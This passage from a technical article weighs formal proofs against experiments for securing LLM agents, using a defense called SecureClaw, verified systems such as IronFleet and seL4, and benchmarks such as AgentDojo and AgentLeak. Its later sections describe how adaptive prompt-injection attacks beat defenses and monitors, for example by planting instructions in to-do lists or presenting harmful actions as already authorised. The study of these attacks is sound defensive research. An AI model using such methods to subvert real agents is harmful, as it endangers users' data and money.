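One property was vacuous even though it passed all three gates. The document-retrieval agent keeps a list of documents it has read and may add only documents from an approved list. The template had fields for tool calls and approved tools, but none for documents. With the barrier on, the model reused those fields, in effect treating each document read as a tool call, so the proof did establish that every document was on the approved list.

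With the barrier off, the model had access to code showing that this agent has no list of approved tools, and it left the template's list of tool calls empty at every step. The property "every tool call is on the approved list" was then true because there were no calls to check, and nothing constrained which documents the agent read. The gates did not detect this because they test the general structure of the proof, which was sound.

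Moon and Varshney propose also checking that each list in a safety property can become non-empty. An engineer can do the same for the invoice assistant by showing that the model has at least one run in which an approved email goes out, because the action guarantee is vacuous if no such run exists.

A specification can also be meaningful but incomplete. IronFleet, another system that Fonseca and colleagues studied, ignores duplicate requests so that a resent request doesn't run twice. They disabled this feature by changing seven lines, and the system still passed verification because the specification didn't require it. IronFleet's developers didn't consider this a bug because, as they understood it, the standard they had proved didn't include the feature, and they added a comment saying so. In an agent that makes payments, the same omission would allow a verified executor to pay an invoice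 twice.

Fonseca and colleagues built a tool that looks for such omissions by disabling random pieces of the implementation and verifying it again. For three IronFleet functions, it needed on average 377, 18 and 8,015 attempts to disable the duplicate check and still pass verification. Moon and Varshney's gates sabotage only the proof, so they can't find a missing requirement this way. Sabotaging the code would probably have exposed the empty list too, because the proof would still have passed without the document check.

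### Where verified systems still fail

Fonseca and colleagues spent more than eight months looking for bugs in IronFleet, Chapar and a third verified system, Verdi. They searched for errors in the protocols that keep the servers consistent, which are very difficult to implement, and found none. In four comparable unverified products, users had reported 12 protocol bugs within a year. The researchers warn against comparing these counts directly, because the unverified products are much larger and have many more users. Even so, finding no protocol bugs in more than eight months is good evidence that verification works for the code it covers.

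They did find 16 bugs elsewhere.

| Where | Bugs | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Unverified code that connects the verified part to the network and disk | 11 | A crash while saving a snapshot loses data |
| Specification | 2 | The photo check that always succeeds |
| Verification tools | 3 | The build tool reports success after the prover crashes |

Most of these bugs were in a few hundred lines of code at the edge of the verified part. In Verdi, a client could put a line break inside a request, and the server would treat the rest as a new command. The same confusion of data and commands makes prompt injection possible. IronFleet had the least unverified code of the three, and the researchers found no bugs of this type in it.

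Another Verdi bug has a direct parallel in SecureClaw. When a recovering server couldn't open its saved data, for example because too many files were open, it assumed that none existed and carried on. An executor that treated its record of used approvals this way would start with an empty record and accept recent approvals again. This could happen even if the proof of the executor's logic were correct, because the logic would be working from the wrong record. The executor should refuse all requests until it can read the record.

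The bugs in the tools are the most unsettling. IronFleet's build tool read only the verifier's first message, which reported no errors, and missed a later one reporting that the prover had crashed. Whenever the prover crashed this way, the tool accepted any program, including one that asserted "false". The bug is relevant to agent frameworks too, because Moon and Varshney follow the method of IronFleet, which is written in Dafny. An easy precaution is to give the tools a false statement before each release and confirm that they reject it.

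Proof assistants such as Isabelle and Lean reduce the risk of accepting an invalid proof by checking every proof with a small kernel. Dafny instead relies on Z3, a large automatic solver, which saves a lot of work but adds more code that has to be correct.

### The assumptions of the seL4 proof

seL4 is a small operating-system kernel with some of the most thorough proofs of any real software. It would be a sensible foundation for SecureClaw, whose four trusted components need something to keep them apart when they share a machine. In the original paper, Klein (2009) and colleagues assumed that the compiler was correct. Since then, the project has added a tool that checks the compiler's output, so on supported processors the compiler is no longer an assumption. seL4's *What the Proofs Assume* lists what remains:

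- **Assembly code:** about 340 lines on ARM processors, mostly for entering and leaving the kernel.
- **Boot code:** about 1,200 lines that run before the kernel reaches its initial state.
- **Hardware:** the processor works as the model predicts, and the kernel manages its caches correctly.
- **Virtual memory:** the kernel's own memory behaves normally while it runs. The developers proved the conditions that they believe ensure this, but no program checked that their list was complete.
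- **Direct memory access:** devices such as network cards, which can write to memory without going through the processor, don't overwrite the kernel.
- **Side channels:** the secrecy proof covers only channels in the model, which leaves out timing.

The developers consider these assumptions much more likely to cause trouble than a mistake in the proof. The list is useful because it is short and specific. A reviewer can read 340 lines of assembly, and an engineer can check which devices have direct access to memory. For the invoice assistant, running on seL4 would replace the assumption that the operating system is secure with these six assumptions. It wouldn't help with a mistake in the gateway's own code.

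### What a proof costs now

Until recently, verifying code took so much work that only a few projects could do it. CompCert, a verified C compiler, took about 3 person-years and 42,000 lines of proof, according to *Machine-Generated Code Deserves Machine-Checked Proofs* (2026). Verifying seL4 took 20 person-years. Kleppmann forecast in *Prediction* (December 2025) that AI would make verification far cheaper. He argued that a language model does no harm by writing a nonsensical proof, because the checker rejects it and the model tries again.

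Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) supports this. Anthropic and Theorem, a formal-methods company, used Claude to prove security properties of the compiled code of 123 open-source libraries. The proofs total 180 million lines (Smith, *Claude Writes 180 Million Lines of Proofs*, 2026). At CompCert's pace, people would have needed almost 13,000 person-years to write that many lines, although their proofs would have been much shorter.

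The specifications came from existing fuzz tests, which run a program on huge numbers of random inputs to find crashes. Claude proved that no input under 64 megabytes crashes any of 239 such test programs when they run on a model of Linux on a RISC-V processor (EconoTimes, *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points*, 2026).

Most servers use x86 processors, which are harder to model. A week after Anthropic's announcement, *Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification* (Leip, 2026) presented a proof that covers a complete x86 program running on Linux. Verifying the compiled program removes the compiler from the trusted core, and the same method works for programs written in any language.

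For SecureClaw, the obvious place to use such proofs is the gateway, which parses files from outsiders. OpenNET's Russian-language article *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026) reports that Claude's work on the libraries uncovered hundreds of bugs, including a buffer overflow in libexpat, a widely used XML parser. A proof that the parser never corrupts memory would rule out a malformed invoice taking over the gateway through a bug like this, but it wouldn't show that the gateway marks the right fields as sensitive.

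The cryptographic part of SecureClaw's argument could also be machine-checked and extended to the running code. *libshrincs* (2026) does this for WOTS+C, a signature scheme in which each key signs only one message. WOTS+C is part of SHRINCS, a larger scheme proposed for Bitcoin. The paper provides a machine-checked proof that WOTS+C is secure, and another proof that the C code behaves like the version in the security proof. Language models wrote most of both proofs under human guidance. The same approach would probably work for SecureClaw's main theorem, since its proof has only two steps and relies on standard properties of authentication codes and fingerprints.

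Even when proofs are easy to produce, people still have to decide what to prove. Tolmach and Klaus (2026), in *The proof is in the spec*, observe that the bottleneck has moved to writing specifications and choosing models and assumptions. Succinct's *An Experiment in Formal Verification with Claude* describes the same shift in a project on cryptographic protocols. Most of the human work went into the statements and definitions, which needed dozens of rounds of careful review. Someone may have to read a thousand lines of Lean for a full protocol, though the team found this much easier than checking every argument by hand.

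A company that buys an agent system can't repeat that review for every product, so the contract should specify exactly what a program has checked. For the invoice assistant's action guarantee, it should list the formal statement, the version of the code it covers, the tools that checked it, and the unverified code on either side of that code. The version matters because a proof about last month's executor doesn't cover yesterday's changes. If the proof is part of the build, a change that breaks it will fail the build until a person or a model repairs the proof.

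## Choosing experiments that support the proof

SecureClaw's theorems don't show whether the executor's code performs the checks in the design, how much data leaks when somebody forgets to mark a field, or how much work the assistant still gets done. Only experiments can answer these questions, and each question needs its own experiment because a result that settles one can be almost irrelevant to another.

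### Attacking the executor directly

The action theorem covers any program that sends requests, so testing it doesn't require a language model. A tester can write the worst requests they can think of and send them straight to the executor. Ma and Schmid built a suite of 29 requests, and the executor refused all 25 invalid ones and accepted the four valid ones. The suite needed valid requests because an executor that refused everything would otherwise have had a perfect score.

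| What is wrong with the request | Cases | Example |
|---|---|---|
| The approval is altered or incomplete | 7 | One bit of the authentication code has changed |
| The request differs from the approved one | 5 | It has a new recipient |
| It comes from the wrong caller or session | 3 | The approval belongs to another session |
| Its context has changed | 3 | It names an extra outside party |
| The time is wrong, or the approval is used up | 3 | The approval has expired |
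| It lacks an identifier or a confirmation | 2 | The user never confirmed the action |
| Two things are wrong at once | 2 | The approval has expired and the text has changed |
| Nothing | 4 | A valid request to a second recipient |

Some of these cases test conditions that the theorem assumes but doesn't prove, for example that the executor rejects expired approvals and requires confirmation for actions that need it. The suite is the only direct evidence of whether the code meets those conditions.

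The result doesn't give a failure rate, because Ma and Schmid chose the cases and the executor is ordinary software that should give the same 29 answers on every run. If the 25 attacks were a random sample, the 95% confidence interval for the failure rate would extend to 13.7%, but attackers don't pick requests at random. An attacker who finds one field that the executor doesn't check can exploit it every time.

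Looking for cases that the suite lacks is more useful. No test in the suite submits two copies of a request at the same moment, or crashes the executor after it marks an approval as used but before it sends the payment, although the theorem assumes that neither event allows a replay. A field missing from the request format, such as the blind-copy field in the last section's example, would also go unnoticed unless a tester thought to change it. An engineer can take the full list of fields from the email service's documentation, change each one after the approval, and check that the executor refuses the request.

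A test that can't fail also provides little evidence. In a separate case study, Ma and Schmid sent the executor one valid payment and four bad ones: a payment raised from $100 to $10,000, a changed payee, a forged approval and a replay. The executor accepted only the valid payment. With its checks switched off, it accepted all five, so the refusals came from the checks and not from an unrelated fault in the requests. A more precise version would switch off one check at a time and confirm that at least one test then fails.

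### Switching off one mechanism at a time

SecureClaw has two main mechanisms. Handles keep raw data away from the model, and the executor requires an approval for every outside action. If the whole system leaks little, either mechanism could be the reason. An ablation study separates their effects by removing one part at a time and repeating the same tasks.

Ma and Schmid ran their experiments on part of AgentLeak, a benchmark in which several agents work together on tasks with private data. It checks for leaks in the messages agents send each other, the memory they share, and the final answer.

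| Configuration | Leaks between agents, under attack | Leaks into shared memory, under attack | Leaks without an attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Full system | 0 of 24 | 0 of 24 | 0 of 24 |
| No approval check | 0 of 24 | 0 of 24 | 0 of 24 |
| No handles | 5 of 24 | 2 of 24 | 4 of 24 |
| Neither | 6 of 24 | 1 of 24 | 4 of 24 |

Leaks between agents occurred only when the handles were removed. The design predicts this, because an approval check on outgoing email does not affect messages between agents.

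Twenty-four tasks is a small sample, though. If handles made no difference and five tasks changed their result by chance, all five would change in the same direction about one time in 16, so the result is suggestive but not conclusive. The 95% interval for 5 of 24 is 7% to 42%, so the size of the effect is very uncertain. The memory figures differ by only one or two tasks, which could easily be chance.

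Results from the full benchmark of 496 attacked scenarios support the same explanation. Faramesh, which checks actions but lets raw data reach the model, leaked data between agents in 92.7% of scenarios and into shared memory in 51.6%, the same rates as an agent with no defence. SecureClaw leaked data between agents in one scenario and into shared memory in none. Faramesh and SecureClaw differ in other ways too, so this comparison can't isolate the effect of the handles as the ablation does, but its sample is 20 times larger.

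The results of the two experiments shouldn't be combined. With both mechanisms off, SecureClaw leaked between agents in 25% of the small sample, far below the 92.7% for an undefended agent on the full benchmark. Ma and Schmid therefore use the small sample only to compare configurations, so its 5 of 24 figure shouldn't be quoted as the leak rate of a system without handles.

Across the three channels, SecureClaw leaked in 16 of the 496 scenarios, and 15 of those leaks were in the assistant's final answer. Handles help least there because the final answer is meant to give someone information.

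### Breaking an assumption on purpose

The data guarantee assumes that the operator has marked every sensitive field. To measure what happens when some are unmarked, Ma and Schmid started from perfect marking, removed marks at random, and reran all of AgentLeak. They counted a leak whenever a protected value appeared in the final answer, a message between agents, or shared memory.

| Protected fields missed | Attacked scenarios with a leak |
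|---|---|
| 0% | 0 of 496 |
| 1% | 18 of 496 (3.6%) |
| 5% | 44 of 496 (8.9%) |
| 10% | 65 of 496 (13.1%) |
| 20% | 85 of 496 (17.1%) |

The gentle slope is misleading for a contract that covers a fully hostile model. The benchmark has about 45 protected fields per task. If each has a 1% chance of losing its mark, the chance that a task has at least one unmarked field is 1 − 0.99^45, or about 36%. Only 3.6% of the attacked scenarios leaked, presumably because the model often didn't read the unmarked field or didn't repeat it. A hostile model would leak every unmarked value it received, so the contract should be based on how often unmarked values reach the model, which could be up to ten times the measured leak rate.

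Real mistakes are also unlikely to be random. For example, if nobody marks a new field on the invoice form, the mistake affects every invoice.

Marking too many fields does far less harm than marking too few, so an operator who is unsure about a field should mark it. When Ma and Schmid wrongly marked up to 20% of the harmless fields, no protected value leaked and the agents still completed about 82% of the tasks. A simple fallback that marked fields based only on the data format also leaked nothing in 996 scenarios and completed 85.9%.

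### Whether the assistant can still do its job

Security guarantees don't measure usefulness, so Dongol says task completion needs a separate check. Ma and Schmid used AgentDojo to compare SecureClaw with CaMeL, which fixes its program before reading untrusted data, and with Progent, which checks each tool call against rules that a language model writes and updates during the task. All three systems used gpt-4o-mini.

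| System | Successful attacks | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed under attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| No defence | 198 of 629 (31.5%) | 68 of 97 (70.1%) | 47.2% |
| Progent | 24 of 629 (3.8%) | 59 of 97 (60.8%) | 53.6% |
| SecureClaw | 4 of 629 (0.6%) | 59 of 97 (60.8%) | 56.6% |
| CaMeL | 0 of 629 | 29 of 97 (29.9%) | 31.0% |

SecureClaw's advantage over Progent in blocking attacks is too large to be chance, but its disadvantage against CaMeL could be chance. If SecureClaw and CaMeL were equally vulnerable, four successful attacks would all be against the same system about one time in eight. The difference in completed tasks is much clearer, since SecureClaw finished twice as many as CaMeL.

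As the first section explained, the four successful attacks don't contradict SecureClaw's theorem, because the policy permitted the actions. An engineer can check this for every successful attack by looking it up in the executor's log. If the log has a genuine approval for that exact request, the policy was too loose. If it doesn't, the code has a bug or an assumption is false. Even one such case shows that the guarantee doesn't hold for the system as built, however many other attacks it blocked.

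The completion figures need more caution than the attack figures. When Ma and Schmid ran SecureClaw again with the same settings, it completed 56.7% of the tasks without an attack instead of 60.8%, so a difference of a few points means little. The score also depends partly on trusted code that replaces references with real values, such as email addresses, in tool calls and before scoring. Without this step, completion fell to 46.4%. The step is reasonable because a deployed system also has to turn references back into real values, but leaving it out would make the comparison rather different.

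When SecureClaw refuses an action, it can suggest a safe next step, such as saving a draft. In a sample of 50 tasks from Agent Security Bench, these suggestions raised task completion from 70% to 86%, and no attack succeeded with or without them.

CaMeL's low score is probably due largely to the small model, which had to write a correct program in advance. With OpenAI's o3 model, CaMeL's designers reported that it completed 77% of AgentDojo tasks, compared with 84% with no defence (quoted in Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026, *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*).

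The choice of tasks matters even more. In *AgentDyn*, Li, Wen and colleagues (2026) counted only 6 tasks among AgentDojo's 97 that force an agent to change its plan along the way. *DRIFT* (2025) reports that CaMeL completed none of those six. Li and colleagues then wrote 60 new tasks that all require replanning, and CaMeL completed none of them with any of the four main models they tested. With GPT-4o, the undefended agent completed 53.3% of the new tasks, but Progent completed only 6.7% because its rules gradually blocked the tools that later steps needed.

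SecureClaw was not tested. Its ordinary tool-calling loop can change plans, which should help, but its policy also has to permit actions that nobody foresaw. A company that wants to know whether the invoice assistant is usable should test it on a few hundred of its own past invoices.

### Reading a zero

On Agent Security Bench, none of 2,000 attacks on SecureClaw succeeded. If each attack independently succeeds with probability p, the chance that all n attacks fail is (1 − p)^n. A two-sided 95% interval leaves out 2.5% at each end, so its upper limit is the value of p that solves

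(1 − p)^n = 0.025

For n = 2,000, this gives the 0.18% in the first section.

| Attacks, none successful | Upper limit for the success rate |
|---|---|
| 24 | 14% |
| 629 | 0.6% |
| 2,000 | 0.18% |
| 3.7 million | One in a million |

Experiments therefore can't come close to the one in 10^50 that a cryptographic bound provides, though that bound holds only if its assumptions do.

The calculation also wrongly treats the attacks as independent draws from everything an attacker might do. The 2,000 cases consist of five styles of planted instruction with 400 cases each. If success depends mostly on the style, the effective sample size is closer to five than to 2,000, and the upper limit on the success rate for a new style is 52%. The AgentDojo run used only one template for all 629 cases.

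Ma and Schmid repeated the 2,000 cases with four other models, and again no attack succeeded. This shows that the result doesn't depend on one particular model. Adding the runs up to "0 of 10,000" would be a mistake, though, because the attacks were the same each time.

An attack success rate of zero also needs a control. Without SecureClaw, the same attacks succeeded 49.8%, 64.6% and 85.4% of the time on three of those models, so the defence had something to stop. In *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026), by contrast, AgentDojo's standard attack succeeded only 0.3% of the time against an undefended Claude Haiku 4.5, so every defence added to that model seemed almost perfect.

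Finally, an attack success rate per attempt understates the danger from an attacker who keeps trying. Narisetty and colleagues cite Anthropic's figures for attacks on Claude Opus 4.5 in coding tasks. The success rate was 4.7% for one attempt, 33.6% for ten and 63.0% for a hundred.

### Attackers who adapt

The benchmarks above use attacks that predate the defence, but a real attacker can study the defence first. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) tested twelve published defences against attackers with this advantage. For most of these defences, the original papers had reported attack success rates near zero. The researchers used automated search and a competition with more than 500 human participants to revise the attack text repeatedly, keeping what worked. The attacks beat all twelve defences and had a success rate above 90% against most of them.

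Those twelve defences relied on wording the prompt carefully, training the model, filtering its input or hiding a secret test in the prompt, all of which depend on a model reacting correctly to hostile text. The study shows that a low score on a fixed benchmark is very weak evidence of security. It doesn't show that systems like SecureClaw would fail, because none of the twelve was a monitor that limits the agent's actions whatever the model outputs.

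Studies in 2026 have started to test monitors too. AutoDojo automates the adaptive attack, allowing only six revisions per target. The only feedback it uses is how often each version succeeds. PIGuard, a classifier that looks for planted instructions, had blocked every fixed attack on a gpt-4o-mini agent, but AutoDojo raised the success rate to 28.0%. Against DRIFT, which combines rules with a language model that judges instructions, the success rate rose from 2.6% to 6.4%. Progent let through 7.7% of attacks. CaMeL was the most effective defence overall, but it also reduced task completion the most on four of the five models.

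*Defending against Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks via Reasoning-enabled Task Alignment* (2026) reports a similar pattern on a small open model, where attack success rates that were low for fixed attacks rose to as much as 50% for adaptive ones against the same defences.

Ma and colleagues also found that vague requests are more dangerous. AutoDojo beat PIGuard 17.3% of the time when the user specified the action and all its details, but 54.2% of the time when the user just told the agent to do whatever was on a to-do list, since an instruction in a to-do list looks normal. AutoDojo succeeded at most 11% of the time against Progent, DRIFT and a third system that restricts actions, for every kind of request, partly because these systems often allowed only read-only tools when the request was vague.

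Narisetty and colleagues, who work for a security company that sells this kind of defence, attacked Progent at its weakest point, the language model that updates its rules. Their adaptive attack presented the harmful action as a routine step that somebody had already authorised. Progent had reduced the success rate of the standard attack from 25.8% to 4.2%, and the adaptive attack succeeded only 2.6% of the time. They interpret this result cautiously because they used one attack template and a small model, and the softer wording may have made the agent less likely to obey.

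None of these studies included SecureClaw. If its theorem's assumptions hold, an adaptive attacker cannot cause an unapproved email to be sent, however many times they revise the attack. They can still search for harmful actions that the policy permits, and all four successful attacks on AgentDojo used such actions. A determined attacker would therefore probably succeed more often than the reported 0.6%, which would not contradict the theorem.

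Narisetty and colleagues say the next experiment should be an attack that uses only authorised actions. For SecureClaw, an engineer could skip the planted text and replace the model with a program that picks the most harmful action the policy allows, which would measure the worst case directly. If the policy lets the assistant send any file to any employee, the program would send the payroll file to the whole company, showing that the policy is too loose without the need for a success rate.

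### The dispute over proofs and experiments

Researchers disagree about whether proofs or experiments deserve more trust. The argument for proof is that only a statement about every attacker covers the attacks that nobody has tried. Dongol makes this point about benchmarks, and Nasr and colleagues agree, although their own work is experimental. In their view, an experiment can never prove a defence robust; researchers can only try as hard as possible to break it and fail. Adaptive attacks beat all twelve defences, which is strong evidence for this position.

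The usual reply is that "every attacker" means every attacker in the threat model. A proof about two interfaces doesn't cover a third one that the designers forgot. Supporters of proof sometimes overstate their case too. Wu and colleagues, who check an agent's actions with a logic solver, wrongly infer that an attacked model can always reach a forbidden state because a model's behaviour is undecidable. Undecidability would mean that no single procedure can settle the question for every model, and a particular model might still never reach such a state. Wu and colleagues also had to run experiments to show that their prototype works.

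Critics of proof go further and say that it mainly moves the risk into the assumptions, which fewer people examine. Cryptographers have argued about this for decades. In *Another Look at "Provable Security"* (2007), Neal Koblitz and Alfred Menezes objected that the phrase implies more than the theorems establish, and they raised three problems relevant here.

**Proofs can be wrong.** In 1994, Mihir Bellare and Phillip Rogaway published OAEP, a way of preparing messages for encryption, with a security proof. Standards had already adopted OAEP when Victor Shoup found a gap in the proof in 2001. Other cryptographers soon repaired the proof for RSA, the case that mattered most in practice.

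**Bounds can be too loose to be useful.** Some proofs show only that breaking a scheme is at most, say, a billion times easier than solving a hard problem, which may guarantee very little at ordinary key lengths.

**A proof's model can omit what the attacker uses.** In 2002, researchers proved that close variants of the encryption in SSH, the standard protocol for logging in to remote servers, were secure. In 2009, Martin Albrecht, Kenneth Paterson and Gaven Watson recovered small pieces of encrypted text from OpenSSH, the most widely used version. The proof treated each message as arriving whole. Real software decrypts a length field first and waits for that many bytes, so an attacker who sends data gradually can learn part of the text from how many bytes the software waits for.

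The first two problems aren't serious for SecureClaw. Its main proof is short enough to check by hand or by machine, and its bound adds the forgery and collision terms without a large multiplying factor. The third problem applies fully. The theorem's game leaves out the executor's reason codes, which are probably harmless, but the people who modelled SSH presumably thought the length field was harmless too. Fonseca and colleagues found the same pattern in verified systems, where the bugs were at the edges of the verified code and not in the protocols that the proofs covered.

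Supporters of proof can answer that the SSH attack led researchers to a better model of the protocol, which included messages that arrive in pieces. After a failure, a proof helps locate the cause, because either one of its assumptions was false or the attack used something the model left out. A failed classifier gives much less guidance, because its developers can train it on the new attack but still don't know which texts will get past it next.

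A proof moves risk into its assumptions, as critics point out, but for an agent system this usually makes testing easier. The tester can check a short list of conditions about ordinary software, most of them with well-understood methods, rather than search through every text that might mislead a model. This benefit is lost if the team treats the theorem as a reason to stop testing. A team with one week left before launching the invoice assistant would probably learn more by looking for a second route to the email service than by testing another 2,000 planted instructions.
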